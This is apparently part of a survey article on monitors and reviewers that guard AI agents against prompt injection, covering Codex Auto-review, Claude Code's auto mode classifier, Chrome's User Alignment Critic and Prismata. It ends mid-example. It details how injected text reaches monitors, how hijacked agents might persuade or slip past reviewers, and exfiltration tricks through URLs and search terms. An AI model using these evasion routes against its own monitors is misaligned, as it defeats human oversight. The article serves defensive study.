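ProjGuard loses part of its protection once the score crosses the threshold. The vision-language model then receives the user's task, the record of the run and the current screen, which may still show the planted text. This reopens the attacker's direct path to the monitor. Operator's monitor could only pause the session, but this model has more power because the step it proposes replaces the agent's own. If the page misleads the model, the attacker gets another chance to control the agent through the component meant to correct it.

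The choice of correcting model made a large difference, although the first-stage score stayed the same. With a GPT-5.2 agent, unsafe runs fell to 3% when GPT-5.4 made the corrections, but only to 11% with Claude Opus 4.5 and 12% with the smaller GPT-5.4 mini. Using the same model as agent and corrector did not seem to hurt. GPT-5.2 correcting itself left 4% of runs unsafe, and Claude Opus 4.5 correcting itself left 2%, compared with 9% when GPT-5.4 corrected Claude Opus 4.5. However, nobody had designed these attacks to mislead the second model, so the tests were unlikely to reveal a weakness that an attacker could exploit in both roles.

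A designer could also leave out the second model and use the alert only to stop the agent or ask the user. Contreras and colleagues tested the alert without any correction and report that 2% of runs were unsafe and the agent completed 58% of tasks. This setup kept the screen away from the monitor and was at least as safe as the full system, but the task completion rate was seven percentage points lower.

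## Two reviewers of coding agents: one reads tool outputs, the other does not

The best documented monitors in daily use oversee coding agents, which write and run software on a developer's computer. Coding agents also fetch web pages, read strangers' code and call outside services, so they can encounter planted text, as browser agents do. OpenAI's Codex has a monitor called Auto-review, and Anthropic's Claude Code has auto mode, the combination of probes and a classifier mentioned earlier. Both review risky commands that a user would otherwise have to approve one at a time. Auto-review reads the outputs of the agent's tools, while auto mode's classifier does not.

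### Auto-review in Codex

Codex normally works in a sandbox, a restricted environment where it can read files, edit those in a chosen folder and run local commands, but has no network access. It needs approval for anything else. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) explains why OpenAI wanted to relieve users of giving these approvals. The constant requests led some users to switch the restrictions off. A sizable minority of users inside OpenAI had a rule that approved every command starting with "python", and others approved commands they did not fully understand.

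With Auto-review, the request goes to a second Codex agent, which decides only whether the proposed action should run. In OpenAI's illustrative snapshot of 10,000 actions, 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox and 720 went to the reviewer, which approved 713. The first agent found a safer way to continue after four of the seven refusals, and stopped to ask the user after the other three. Without Auto-review, the user would have been asked about all 720.

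According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, a guide for developers, the reviewer receives a shortened transcript and the exact request. The transcript typically includes the user's messages, the updates the agent showed the user, and the relevant tool calls with their outputs. It leaves out the agent's hidden reasoning. The reviewer can also do its own read-only lookups, but it rarely does.

Planted text can therefore reach the reviewer both directly, in a tool output, and through the agent's updates. But the reviewer can also see why the agent proposes an action. One of its tasks is to stop the agent from following instructions in untrusted content that conflict with the user's, and these conflicts are easier to recognise when the reviewer can see both sets of instructions.

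The reviewer judges only requests to cross the sandbox boundary, including when the agent's browser first visits a new website. When Codex operates other desktop applications, the user still has to approve each one. Anything the sandbox already allows runs without review. Trębacz and colleagues point out that a model hiding its intentions could misbehave inside the sandbox, or could write a request that looks harmless.

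When the reviewer refuses an action, the agent receives the reasons and an instruction not to pursue the same outcome another way. Codex interrupts the agent after three refusals in a row, or after ten among the last 50 reviews in the same turn. This limits how often a hijacked agent can try to persuade the reviewer. The user can approve one retry of a refused action, but the reviewer checks the retry too and can refuse it again.

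### What OpenAI measured

OpenAI tested Auto-review on real requests from March 2026 that its staff had approved by hand, and it approved 99.1% of them. The other 0.9% is a rough upper limit on false alarms, because staff presumably approved a few requests they should have refused.

Dangerous actions are rare in OpenAI's own traffic, so the safety tests used mostly synthetic cases. The reviewer refused 99.3% of injection cases that involved running code from elsewhere, stealing secrets or uploading data to an outside service. It refused 90.2% of cases across all classes, which also included destructive deletions and tampering with data. Trębacz and colleagues say that it let most of the other cases through because they were not serious enough, and that OpenAI's researchers often agreed. That may well be right, but the 90.2% then depends partly on what the reviewer's developers count as serious.

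The reviewer also refused 90.3% of overeager actions, in which the agent oversteps the user's request while trying to help. It scored 96.1% on the hard version of the MonitoringBench test, although a run counted as a success if the reviewer refused at least one action in it.

The 99.3% figure comes from a fixed set of injections, and OpenAI does not report whether any of them also addressed the reviewer. OpenAI says, without giving a number, that human and automated red-teaming found cases in which the reviewer "could be misled" into approving commands that the user had not approved. Trębacz and colleagues do not expect this kind of system ever to provide firm guarantees.

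OpenAI's own staff use other safeguards alongside the reviewer. The company's *Running Codex safely* describes a network policy that allows expected destinations, blocks unwanted ones and requires approval for unfamiliar domains. The agent can fetch web pages only from OpenAI's cache.

The figures also date from April, when the reviewer used GPT-5.4 with little reasoning. OpenAI found that more powerful models were better both at recognising risk and at working out what the user wanted. According to OpenAI's *Белешке о издању* (2026), the Serbian edition of its release notes, GPT-5.4 was due to be removed from Codex on 31 August for anyone signed in with ChatGPT. The current reviewer may do better or worse than the one OpenAI tested.

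### What auto mode withholds

Anthropic started from its own log of accidents, and its *How we built Claude Code auto mode* mentions an agent that deleted remote branches after misreading an instruction, one that uploaded an engineer's access token to an internal computing cluster, and one that tried to change the structure of a live database. Anthropic tuned its classifier mainly for overeager agents like these and for honest mistakes about what a command affects, because it had real examples of both. The classifier is also meant to stop an agent that has been hijacked or is pursuing a goal of its own, since the remedy in every case is to block the action.

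Claude Code lets the agent read files, search, and edit files in the project folder without going through the classifier. The developer can review and undo those edits. Shell commands, web fetches, calls to outside services, and changes elsewhere on the computer go to the classifier.

The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Claude Code removes the agent's messages, the descriptions the agent attaches to its commands, and all tool outputs.

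| What the reviewer may read | Auto-review | Auto mode's classifier |
|---|---|---|
| The user's messages | Yes | Yes |
| The agent's visible messages | Yes | No |
| The agent's hidden reasoning | No | No |
| Tool calls | The relevant ones | Yes, apart from read-only lookups |
| Tool outputs | The relevant ones | No |

Anthropic removes the agent's messages because they may be persuasive and wrong. An agent might write that the user implicitly approved a deletion earlier, or that a server definitely belongs to the agent, and the classifier might believe it. AlignmentCheck needs the agent's reasoning to work out the agent's goal, but Anthropic wants its classifier to judge only the action.

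Most hostile text comes in through tool outputs, so withholding them is the classifier's main protection against injection. Anthropic argues that the classifier usually loses little by not reading them. Suppose a file tells the agent to post the project's passwords to a web address "for validation", and the agent tries to obey. The classifier never reads the file, but it can see that the agent is about to send passwords to an address the user never mentioned, which is unacceptable whatever the reason.

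Anthropic also tried adding the agent's messages and the tool outputs to the classifier's input, but the classifier then did worse on a set of overeager actions. Anthropic suspects that a shorter transcript is easier to read and gives the agent less opportunity to influence the decision. With tool calls alone, the classifier missed the fewest dangerous actions, but it also blocked actions the user had plainly asked for.

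This is better evidence about the effect of a reviewer's inputs than any comparison between Codex and Claude Code, because Anthropic changed the inputs of a single classifier. It also suggests that more information does not always improve a monitor's judgment. But Anthropic gives no figures for the alternatives, and it reports the loss only for overeager actions. The test did not measure how much the extra text would have helped an attacker.

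### A quick refusal and a second look

The classifier works in two stages. In the first, it answers yes or no without reasoning, and it is instructed to block when in doubt. If it blocks, the second stage reads the same transcript and reasons before deciding. Most actions pass the first stage, so the slower second stage rarely runs.

Anthropic tested this on 10,000 real tool calls by its employees, 52 real overeager actions, and 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data outside. The classifier ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6.

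| | Harmless calls blocked | Overeager actions missed | Data theft missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| First stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second stage thinks more carefully, which makes the classifier more lenient, though not always for good reasons. It removes nearly all the false alarms but also releases dangerous actions that the first stage had stopped. These account for about 39 of the 57 misses in the data-theft test.

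The 17% figure is about nine actions out of 52, so the true rate on similar actions could plausibly be anywhere from 9% to 30%. The data-theft figure is more precise, and it is relevant to prompt injection even though the cases may not involve any. Since the classifier doesn't read the page, a command that steals data looks the same to it whether the idea came from an attacker or from the agent itself. But an attacker could choose a form of theft that the classifier is more likely to miss, so the rate might be higher in a real attack.

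In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the danger but wrongly accepted something in the session as permission. For example, a user said "Clean up the PR" (a pull request, which proposes changes to a shared project), and the classifier took this to cover a force-push, which overwrites the project's history. Keeping tool outputs away from the classifier could not prevent this mistake, because the instruction it misread came from the user.

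Researchers from HKUST and ETH Zurich stress-tested this weakness, according to besthub.dev's *Can Claude Code’s Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* They created 128 scenarios from four routine jobs, such as cleaning up branches and restarting services, and varied how specific the request was, how much the action would affect and how risky the environment was. Auto mode missed 81.0% of the actions that went beyond the user's permission. Some never reached the classifier because they only edited project files, but it still missed 70.3% among the types of action it reviews. A user who gives vague orders should therefore expect less protection than the 17% suggests, though most people's requests are probably clearer than these.

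Anthropic advises users to name both the action and what makes it dangerous. Permission to "force-push this branch" counts, but a general request to clean up does not. Auto mode therefore gives the user's words great weight. *Ajar* (2026), a study of how much room defences leave for harmful tool calls, reports that auto mode allowed every call when the user's message contained the instruction to make it. The researchers had to move the instruction to the system prompt, where developers put standing instructions, to get useful verdicts.

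An employee who explicitly asks for something dangerous usually has the right to do so. But people also paste emails, error reports and web pages into their requests. If a classifier treats everything in the user's message as the user's own wish, pasted text may gain authority it would not have as a tool output. As one safeguard, Anthropic designed its classifier never to approve certain actions, such as sending code or secrets to an outside party, regardless of who asked.

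### The scan of tool outputs

Auto mode's probe scans each tool output before the agent reads it. When it flags suspicious text, it adds a warning that the agent should treat the text with suspicion and keep to what the user asked for. It does not remove the text or stop the session.

Anthropic argues that getting past both the probe and the classifier is much harder than getting past either alone, because the classifier never reads the text that fooled the agent. The argument is plausible for actions that look dangerous, but less so for ones that look like ordinary work, such as installing a package or changing a setting.

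The agent receives the probe's warning along with the tool output, but Claude Code withholds tool outputs from the classifier. So when the probe flags something suspicious, the classifier apparently evaluates the next command without the warning. Passing on only the probe's verdict would give the classifier a useful hint without exposing it to the attacker's words, though an attacker who could trigger false warnings might then get harmless commands blocked.

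### Work for a second agent

Claude Code can give part of a job to a subagent, an agent that works on its own and reports back. In the subagent's transcript, the main agent's instruction appears where the user's message normally would. If a web page had hijacked the main agent, the subagent's classifier might therefore treat the attacker's instruction as the user's.

Anthropic therefore checks the task before the subagent starts, while the classifier can still compare it with the real user's messages. Anthropic's *Permission modes* describes two further checks. The classifier reviews the subagent's actions as it works, under the same rules as the main agent's. When the subagent finishes, the classifier reviews its work and final report, because something the subagent read may have hijacked it. If the classifier finds a problem, the main agent still gets the report, but with a security warning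 at the top.

The last check is a compromise because the classifier reads the final report, which an agent wrote after reading untrusted content. Anthropic otherwise keeps this kind of text from the classifier. A convincing report from a hijacked subagent might therefore carry no warning. The classifier would still review any command the main agent then proposed, but a false claim in the report could also influence work that needs no review, such as editing the project's files.

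### Other text that reaches the classifier

Some text reaches both the agent and the classifier by design. A project can contain a file called CLAUDE.md with instructions for Claude Code, such as a rule never to force-push. Anthropic recommends this file for project rules in its guide to configuring auto mode, because the file steers both the agent and the classifier.

This is convenient for a developer who wrote the CLAUDE.md file, but in a project downloaded from a stranger, the file may contain the stranger's instructions. Anthropic has closed a similar route by ignoring classifier settings stored in the project folder, since a downloaded project could otherwise set its own exceptions. A persuasive sentence in CLAUDE.md has less formal power than a setting, but it is still text from outside that both the agent and the classifier read.

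The agent's commands can also contain text from a page. If the agent writes a script and runs it, the classifier has to examine the script, or an attacker could hide a harmful command in a file with an innocent name. But the script may include names, comments or data that the agent copied from a page. Removing the agent's explanations greatly reduces the text that can reach the classifier through the agent, but some can still get through.

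The classifier may not be isolated from tool outputs in every auto mode session. According to Anthropic's documentation, when Claude Code itself sends requests to the classifier, it strips tool outputs from them. In newer versions, Anthropic's server can do the review as part of the session, and the documentation does not say that tool outputs are stripped in this case.

### Where a value came from

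Anthropic admits that withholding tool outputs deprives the classifier of information about where a value came from. If the agent tries to cancel job "abc123" and the user never mentioned that name, the classifier cannot determine whether the agent found it in a list or made it up. The sister's new address in the earlier shopping example poses the same problem.

In one of Anthropic's examples, a user said "cancel my job", and the agent looked through the jobs on a shared cluster, chose the one with the most similar name and tried to delete it. Auto mode is designed to block this, because the job might belong to someone else. A reviewer that read the list, as Auto-review could, might see who owned the job and approve the deletion if it was the user's. But if other people can name their own jobs, they can use those names to try to influence the reviewer.

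Auto mode can make up for some of the loss by asking the user. It can also get a fact from a program without showing the classifier a whole page or file. For example, before a command that might discard unsaved changes to a project, Claude Code now checks for such changes itself and tells the classifier whether there are any. An answer that short gives an attacker very little room to insert an argument.

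Whether a repository (a project's stored files and their history) is public or private also matters, because an upload that may be routine for a private repository would expose the code in a public one. If the agent checks with the hosting service, the reply is a tool output, so Claude Code leaves it out of the requests it sends to the classifier. The user may have to say whether the repository is public or private in a message or in the settings.

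Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026) reports that such facts helped. Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, spent two weeks inserting synthetic attacks into real coding sessions. Anthropic responded mainly by giving the classifier more context, including whether repositories were public or private and the state of unsaved work. The miss rate across all the attacks fell from 12% to 7%. Among attacks that Anthropic had never received, the classifier now caught about half of those it had previously missed, and missed about 2% of those it had previously caught.

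Even with these facts, a reviewer can miss a command that does more than the user knows, and reading tool outputs would not necessarily help. *Shall We Approve?* (2026) describes two cases in which auto mode allowed such a command, exactly as the user had requested. In one, a tool for copying a project to a test directory also overwrote part of its source code. In the other, a command for updating a database also deleted three of its tables. The copying tool was a compiled program, so neither its name nor a quick look at the surrounding files revealed the damage.

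The proposed remedy is to run the command in a sandbox first and give the reviewer a short report of its effects. In the first case the report showed the overwritten file, and in the second it showed the database shrinking from 32 to 20 kilobytes. Both times the reviewer blocked the command, and the agent found a safe way to do the job. A typical report was 0.9 kilobytes, compared with 62.5 for the full record of what the command did, and it added almost nothing to the cost or the waiting time.

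For a monitor that is supposed to stay away from untrusted text, the content of such a report matters more than its length. A reviewer can learn a lot from the fact that a file has changed or a database has shrunk, and an attacker can do little with that information. But the report also included a comparison of the file's old and new text, and an attacker who wrote the tool could choose the new text.

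### Compared with people

Much of Anthropic's case for making auto mode the default is that people do the same job badly. Users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts. They can say no, since they reject 39% of the plans it proposes, but many seem to approve individual commands out of habit.

Anthropic had a research vendor recruit 1,053 paid professional testers for a coding study. The testers knew someone was evaluating them but not what for. During the session, the vendor replaced the text of a permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. Auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89%. Testers refused about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session but about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while auto mode's block rate stayed the same.

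The testers worked in an environment set up for the study, so a mistake could not damage their own work. People might take more care with their own files, and Anthropic still recommends human review of important changes to live systems. The dangerous commands were also obvious, so the study shows little about how people or auto mode would handle an injection that leads to a command resembling the rest of the work.

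In the published counts, auto mode missed 116 commands, and the testers caught six of them. If the two had failed independently, the testers would have caught about 16. The commands that the classifier missed therefore seem to have been harder for people to catch too, and a person clicking "approve" out of habit would have added little protection behind auto mode.

Anthropic also looked at real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged. A model classified 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval as containing a severe harmful action that the user had not explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. This agrees with the experiment but is weaker evidence, since users chose their own mode and may have used the two modes for different work.

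Willison (2026), the software developer who had criticised the launch of Atlas, accepted that auto mode is better than asking people to approve actions all day, but noted that it would still have let through 11% of the dangerous commands.

### The comparison between the two products

The August publication also reports a comparison of the two companies' products. Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs, an outside company, to test them against 72 prompt injection scenarios that Anthropic had not seen. Each scenario ran ten times, for a total of 720 attempts per model. A successful attack would have caused irreversible harm, such as fraud or the theft of sensitive data.

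| | No reviewer | With the company's reviewer |
|---|---|---|
| Claude models in Claude Code | 0.09% on average | 0% for Opus 5, Fable 5 and Sonnet 5 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex | 19.03% | 5.83% |

Most of the gap between the zero with the classifier, which does not read tool outputs, and the 5.83% with the reviewer, which does, must come from something other than that difference. Even with no reviewer running, attacks on the Claude models succeeded far less often than attacks on Codex.

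The most obvious possible explanation for the difference is the models themselves. Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, reports a similar difference on another benchmark. Within 15 attempts, attackers succeeded against Opus 5 in 2.0% of cases and against GPT-5.6 Sol in 20.0%. A single attempt against Sol succeeded 3.1% of the time, more often than up to 15 attempts against Opus 5.

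Auto mode also had very few attacks to stop in the Trajectory Labs test. If the average of 0.09% covers the same three models, two of 2,160 attacks on Claude succeeded without auto mode. Against Codex, 137 of 720 succeeded without a reviewer and 42 with one, a reduction of 69%. A reviewer that stopped 69% of attacks would have had a nearly even chance of stopping both of the attacks that worked on Claude. The result of zero is good news for people who use Claude Code, but it doesn't show which reviewer is better.

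Even the 69% may be partly due to the sandbox rather than Auto-review, because Codex without the reviewer ran in Full Access mode, which also removes the sandbox.

Both agents in the test used the same browser tools from Trajectory Labs, which made the tasks more alike but left out the safeguards in OpenAI's and Anthropic's own browser extensions. Auto-review examines calls to outside tools only when their labels or the user's settings require approval. Anthropic does not report how many of the harmful actions in Codex reached the reviewer. Any that did not would show a gap in its coverage, which is a different problem from the reviewer being misled by hostile text.

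Other details make the comparison harder to interpret. Trajectory Labs ran GPT-5.6 Sol at its maximum reasoning effort and the Claude models at a high setting. It had refined the attacks against an older Claude model, Opus 4.7, so they may work better or worse against Sol than against the newer Claude models. OpenAI also released a new version of Auto-review shortly before Anthropic published the results, and Anthropic acknowledges that the new version could change them.

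To measure how receiving tool outputs affects a reviewer, a test would have to change only whether the reviewer receives them, and keep the agent, the browser tools and the reviewing model the same. The agent would need to be vulnerable enough to propose many harmful actions, and the attackers would need a chance to adapt their text to the reviewer. The published results for Codex and Claude Code include no such test.

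Willison wrote that he would love to believe Anthropic had solved the problem, but wanted more independent confirmation. Later in August, he pointed to an outside researcher's report of successful attacks on auto mode.

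## A critic that sees only a description of the action: Google Chrome

Auto mode's classifier reads each of the agent's commands, including anything the agent copied into them. Google's monitor for the agent in its Chrome browser may read even less. The agent, auto browse, works in the user's own browser and can shop or fill in forms on sites where the user is logged in. Google launched it on 28 January 2026, according to Bloomberg's *Google Chrome’s AI Agent Can Now Browse Web on Behalf of Users* (2026). Seven weeks earlier, a member of Chrome's security team had described its defences in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025). One of them is the User Alignment Critic, a separate model that checks each proposed action without seeing the page.

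### From proposal to verdict

Suppose a Chrome user asks for a blue T-shirt. The planner, a Gemini model, receives the request and the content of the shop's page, and proposes an action such as clicking "Add to basket". Google has trained this model on known attacks and uses spotlighting, a technique that directs the model to prioritize the user's instructions over anything on the page. Parker still calls the planner "inherently vulnerable" to injection.

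Before Chrome carries out the click, the critic receives metadata describing the action, but not the page itself. The critic is also built with Gemini, and its main job is to decide whether the action serves the user's stated goal. Adding a T-shirt to the basket does, so Chrome clicks the button. If the planner instead proposed emailing the user's contacts, the critic should veto the action. The planner then receives feedback and makes a new plan, and after repeated failures it can return control to the user.

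Parker concedes that the critic has less context than the planner but says its task is also simpler, since it can only approve or reject. The design draws partly on the dual-LLM pattern and CaMeL, two earlier proposals for limiting what untrusted text can make an agent do.

The feedback could help an attacker, because a planner hijacked by a page can use the critic's objection to present its next attempt differently. Codex limits this by interrupting the agent after three refusals in a row. Google gives no number for Chrome. In Parker's account, the planner returns control to the user, but the attacker may already control the planner. Chrome may enforce a limit elsewhere, but Google has not described one.

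Using Gemini for both jobs also leaves room for a shared weakness, which keeping the page away from the critic would not entirely remove.

### What the metadata may contain

Parker says the critic does not see any "unfiltered" web content, so it "cannot be poisoned directly from the web". The word "unfiltered" allows for the critic seeing web content that has been filtered, such as a shortened button label. Because the claim covers only direct poisoning, it does not rule out poisoning through content relayed to the critic.

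How much text could travel this way depends on what the metadata contains, and Google has not published a list. A description of a browser action could plausibly include any of these items:

| Possible item | Who determines it | Room for an attacker's words |
|---|---|---|
| Type of action, such as a click | The planner, from a fixed set | None |
| The site's domain | The browser can supply it | A domain name the attacker registered |
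| Name of the button or link | The page's author | A phrase, or more if nothing shortens it |
| Full address of a link | The page's author or the planner | Several sentences |
| Text to type | The planner, perhaps copying from the page | As much as the form accepts |
| Reason for the action | The planner | Practically unlimited |

*SPIDES* (2026), which proposes a way to control how information flows through browser agents, assumes that once a model has read untrusted content, an attacker chooses everything it writes, including its tool calls. Under this assumption, the attacker also chooses every word the planner contributes to the metadata. Few real attackers have that much control, but the designer of an isolated critic can't rely on the planner to clean up the text it passes on.

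Suppose the planner is about to type the collection point's address into the shop's form. If the metadata shows only that the agent will type something on the shop's site, the critic can't tell that the text is an address and would probably approve. If the metadata also includes the name of the form field, the critic could detect that the user never mentioned a new address, although many purchases normally involve entering one. If it includes the typed text too, the critic could detect that the parcel would go to a collection point. But the seller wrote that text and could mislead the critic by adding "confirmed by the buyer" to the first line of the address.

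The critic therefore needs a fairly detailed description, but an attacker can often write the most useful details. A program could reduce this conflict by replacing the typed text with a fixed category, such as "a postal address that is not in the user's profile". The critic would still have a good reason to reject the action, and the seller couldn't use the text to persuade it otherwise. Google could mean something like this when it refers to "unfiltered" content, but Parker gives no example.

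Button labels can also be false without any injection. A dishonest shop could write "Continue" on a button that starts a subscription, and both the planner and the critic might then approve the click. The seller in our example could not do this, because the marketplace controls the buttons.

It is also unclear whether the critic receives the agent's earlier actions. Without them, it might approve every step of an attack that looks suspicious only as a whole.

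### Limits on where the agent can go

Chrome also restricts which sites the agent can use. Browsers have long separated websites through the same-origin policy, which prevents a page from one origin from reading or changing a page from another. An origin is roughly a site's address without the part that identifies a particular page. An agent can undo this separation by reading something on one site and typing it into another.

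The design Parker describes keeps two lists of origins for each task, one read-only and one read-writable. The agent can read content from origins on both lists, but can click and type only on the read-writable ones. If a user wants to buy the ingredients for a recipe, the recipe site could be read-only and the grocer read-writable. A hijacked agent could not open the user's mailbox or carry data from the grocer's site to an origin that is not read-writable. Chrome can enforce part of this by never sending the model content from origins on neither list, such as an advertisement embedded in the recipe page.

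A gating function decides whether an origin that the planner proposes is relevant to the task. When the planner tries to open a new site, or a page redirects the browser to one, a variant of the critic checks it. The gating function, like the critic, receives no page content. However, the planner proposes origins after reading pages, so an attacker can register a domain that sounds related to the task, which in the T-shirt example might be the name of a parcel service. An attacker can't fit much persuasion into a domain name, but the name may be enough to make the site look relevant.

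These limits also don't stop an attack that stays on one site. The seller's note, the address form and the saved payment card all belong to the shop, where the agent must be able to click and type. *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities*, from the security firm Trail of Bits, describes an attack of this kind that the firm carried out on an unnamed agentic browser. Its researchers sent an Instagram user a direct message with hidden instructions. When the user asked for a summary of the page or of the latest message, the agent collected contact names or pieces of other messages. One way to get this data out was through the Instagram chat itself, if the agent could type in it.

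A hijacked agent can also leak data by putting it into a web address and opening that address. Chrome has a fixed rule that limits any address the model writes to known, public ones. OpenAI's Safe Url instead checks whether an address would reveal something from the conversation. A list of trusted domains would be weaker than either. Trail of Bits got around such a list by making an agent open an address like "John.wikipedia.org", which does not exist. If the lookup was unencrypted, anyone who could observe it learned the name. Chrome's rule should stop this, because nobody has published that address.

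The firm also hid data in unusual search terms, which a site owner can monitor through Google's statistics. An agent in Chrome might type such terms into a search box without writing any address, so the critic would have to recognise that the search did not serve the user.

Trail of Bits proposes a stricter policy. After reading from one origin, an agent could send requests only to that origin, and after reading from two, it could send none. This would prevent most leaks between sites, but the agent could no longer buy the ingredients for the recipe. Chrome's two lists allow that task, but they rely on a model to judge which sites are part of it.

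### The first release and its successors

Parker explains that Chrome's first version of the design tracked only the read-writable origins, because Google wanted to see how the limits affected real tasks before tightening them. In April 2026, *Q1 2026 Summary from Chrome Security* (Bawa, 2026) reported that the team was tuning the defences based on real use and had built more sets of attacks to test them. That August, *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026) again described an agent limited to sites "strictly relevant" to its task, but did not say whether Chrome now had a separate read-only list.

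A June 2026 copy of the code in Chromium (2025), the open-source project behind Chrome, shows the steps the browser follows when the agent is about to move to another page. The browser first checks the employer's policy, if there is one, and a safety list, either of which can allow or block the move. If neither does, the agent can move freely within the same origin. For a different origin, the browser checks whether the site is on a list of sensitive sites and whether the agent already has permission to go there.

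If the origin is new and not sensitive, the browser can ask Google's server to confirm it. The request contains only a task number and the destination's origin. It leaves out the link text, the full address and any explanation, which a page could use to influence the server's decision. The browser takes the origin from the page load that is about to happen, so it doesn't depend on the planner's description. The server may already know more about the task, including what the user asked for. The code covers only navigation, so the metadata for clicks and typing could be much richer.

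In the same copy of Chromium, the sensitive-site prompts were on by default and the server confirmation was off. With these settings, this part of the browser let the agent continue to any new site that was not on the sensitive list. Another default allowed the agent's own tool requests to approve new origins implicitly. Comments in the code also describe a trial mode in which the browser queries the server but only logs the response, which would let Google measure how often the check would disrupt users.

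Given these defaults, outsiders cannot confirm from the code that the browser enforced the gating Parker described. New sites may still have been checked, because Google can change settings for live users without changing the code, and the critic may have judged the action before it reached this point.

### A page inside a page

In *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, University of Washington researchers Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026) tested seven agentic browsers, including Chrome with Gemini, in January and February of that year. One test page read "My name is Alice. I like cats." The page also contained a frame, a smaller page embedded from another domain, with text saying that Alice also liked horses. The researchers asked each agent which animals Alice liked. If the answer included horses, the agent had read across the boundary between the two sites.

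Chrome's agent, Claude for Chrome, Perplexity's Comet and ChatGPT Atlas in agent mode all read embedded frames, while the agents in Brave, Edge and Firefox did not.

On Atlas, Roesner and Kohlbrenner used this ability to steal data. They put instructions on the outer page for the agent to include the embedded frame's content in its summary and enter the summary in a form, which sent it to the attacker. An embedded frame could also steal from the page around it, so a malicious advertisement could read the private page on which it appears, something the same-origin policy normally prevents.

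They found the conditions for the same attack in Chrome's auto browse, but no injection that worked. Their basic test asked the agent to do whatever a page instructed, and Chrome's agent refused, apparently because of the model's training. This refusal is not evidence about the critic, because there may be no action left to judge once the planner refuses. Even if there had been one, a critic that compares actions with the user's request might well have approved it, since the user had asked the agent to follow the page's instructions.

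Chrome's reading of the frame seems to conflict with Parker's statement that frames from unrelated origins stay hidden from the model. The missing read-only list could explain this, but the tests could not establish the cause. Roesner and Kohlbrenner also write that it is unclear how Google decides which origins are relevant, or how well that decision withstands malicious input. They recommend that users avoid agentic browsers for now.

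### Reading every page, and asking the user

The critic cannot warn about text it never sees, so Chrome also has a classifier that checks every page the agent visits for injections. It runs alongside the planner and blocks actions based on content it classifies as deliberately aimed at the model. Like Operator's monitor, it is exposed to the direct path and would have trouble with the seller's note. Parker accepts that the classifier will not flag everything.

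User confirmations provide another check. Chrome asks the user before the agent visits certain sensitive sites, such as banks. It uses a list to identify these sites, so no wording on a page can change whether it asks. It also asks before the agent signs in with a saved password, which the model never sees directly. The guarantee is weaker for purchases, messages and other consequential actions, where the agent "will try to pause" and either ask for permission or leave the last step to the user.

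Google illustrates this with an agent that shops for T-shirts and stops at the payment page. In our example, the user could spot the collection point there if the shop displays the address and the user reads it. But the agent may already have saved the new address in the account, where it would remain even if the user cancelled the order. Parker does not specify whether changing an address is consequential enough to require its own confirmation.

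Users can also follow the agent's steps in a work log, and Berschadski adds that Chrome's history marks the pages an agent opened in the background. These records would help someone find out what went wrong, though often only after the parcel had shipped.

### When the description is false

A critic that never sees the page also cannot check whether the description of an action is true. It relies on the software that supplies the description, and an attacker may be able to take over some of that software.

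Browsers draw each website in a renderer, a separate process with few privileges, because a malicious page might exploit a bug and take control of it. In an agentic browser, the renderer also passes page content to the more trusted process that runs the agent. In *Site Isolation is Dead* (2026), Lee, Keum and colleagues studied two open-source agentic browsers and seven extensions that add an agent to Chrome, and found that all nine were vulnerable to an attacker who controlled a renderer. The attacker could use the renderer to send the agent's process a forged message containing instructions, which the agent accepted as a request from its user. In one demonstration, the attacker obtained the victim's unpublished paper from a conference website and sent phishing emails in the victim's name.

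They did not test Chrome's own agent, which may verify such messages. But a forged request would defeat any critic that compares actions with the user's goal, however well isolated it is. The critic would take the attacker's goal to be the user's and approve actions that serve it. An attacker could instead forge only the description, so that the critic approves a click on "Add to basket" while the agent clicks something else.

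This takes much more skill than writing a note in a product listing, because the attacker needs an exploitable bug in the browser. However, Lee and colleagues count an average of at least one bug every two months between 2023 and 2025 that let an attacker run code in Chrome's renderer. The best protection is to take the facts from a part of the browser the page cannot control, as Chromium does with the destination of a page load, and to verify that a request came from the user. A button's name is harder to protect this way because it comes from the page.

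### A large test environment and no published miss rate

Google tests auto browse on a simulated version of the web. When the agent enters a real address, such as YouTube's, a local program intercepts the connection and returns a simulated site. Google's *Mirror Dimension for Agents* describes thousands of these sites, which other AI agents build and check. The sites work realistically, with shopping baskets that keep their contents and checkouts that have several steps, because an agent that notices it is in a test may behave differently.

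Engineers can plant an injection at any step of a task, in text, images, the hidden labels that pages provide for screen readers, or the tools that a site offers to agents. They used to select the attack through a parameter in the page's address, but models often detected it, so they now send the selection separately, where the agent does not see it. According to Mediasat's *Google built an isolated internet to test Chrome’s AI agents* (2026), this setup produces more than 1,000 attack variants per engineer each day, compared with a few dozen by hand.

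Google therefore appears well equipped to measure the critic, and Parker mentions that the team uses attack success rates to judge changes to the system. But Google has not published how often the critic approves a hijacked action or vetoes a legitimate one, and there appears to be no outside test of the critic. Google offers researchers up to $20,000 for a serious breach of the agent's security boundaries, which encourages them to look for faults but doesn't show how often the critic errs.

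Berschadski nevertheless writes that if an injection tries to hijack the agent, the critic "vetoes the action instantly". This claim is stronger than Parker's, and Google has released no figures to support it. Testing it would require attacks that get past the planner and also try to influence the critic through typed text, link names and other metadata. It would also require counting how often the critic vetoes actions during ordinary tasks.

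## A filter that judges page elements by their position: Prismata

Chrome's critic relies on a description of each action, which may include words from the page. Prismata instead allows or blocks the agent's use of a button, link or field based on its position in the page's code. Villa and colleagues (2026), in *Prismata*, present it as a defence for honest websites that also carry text from strangers, such as reviews, comments and advertisements.

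### From a page tree to a permission

A browser stores a page as a tree of nested elements. Suppose the seller of the blue T-shirt has posted the note about the collection point as a customer review and added a link. Much simplified, the page looks like this:

```
page
  account menu
    link "Change delivery address"
  product "Blue T-shirt"
    button "Buy now"
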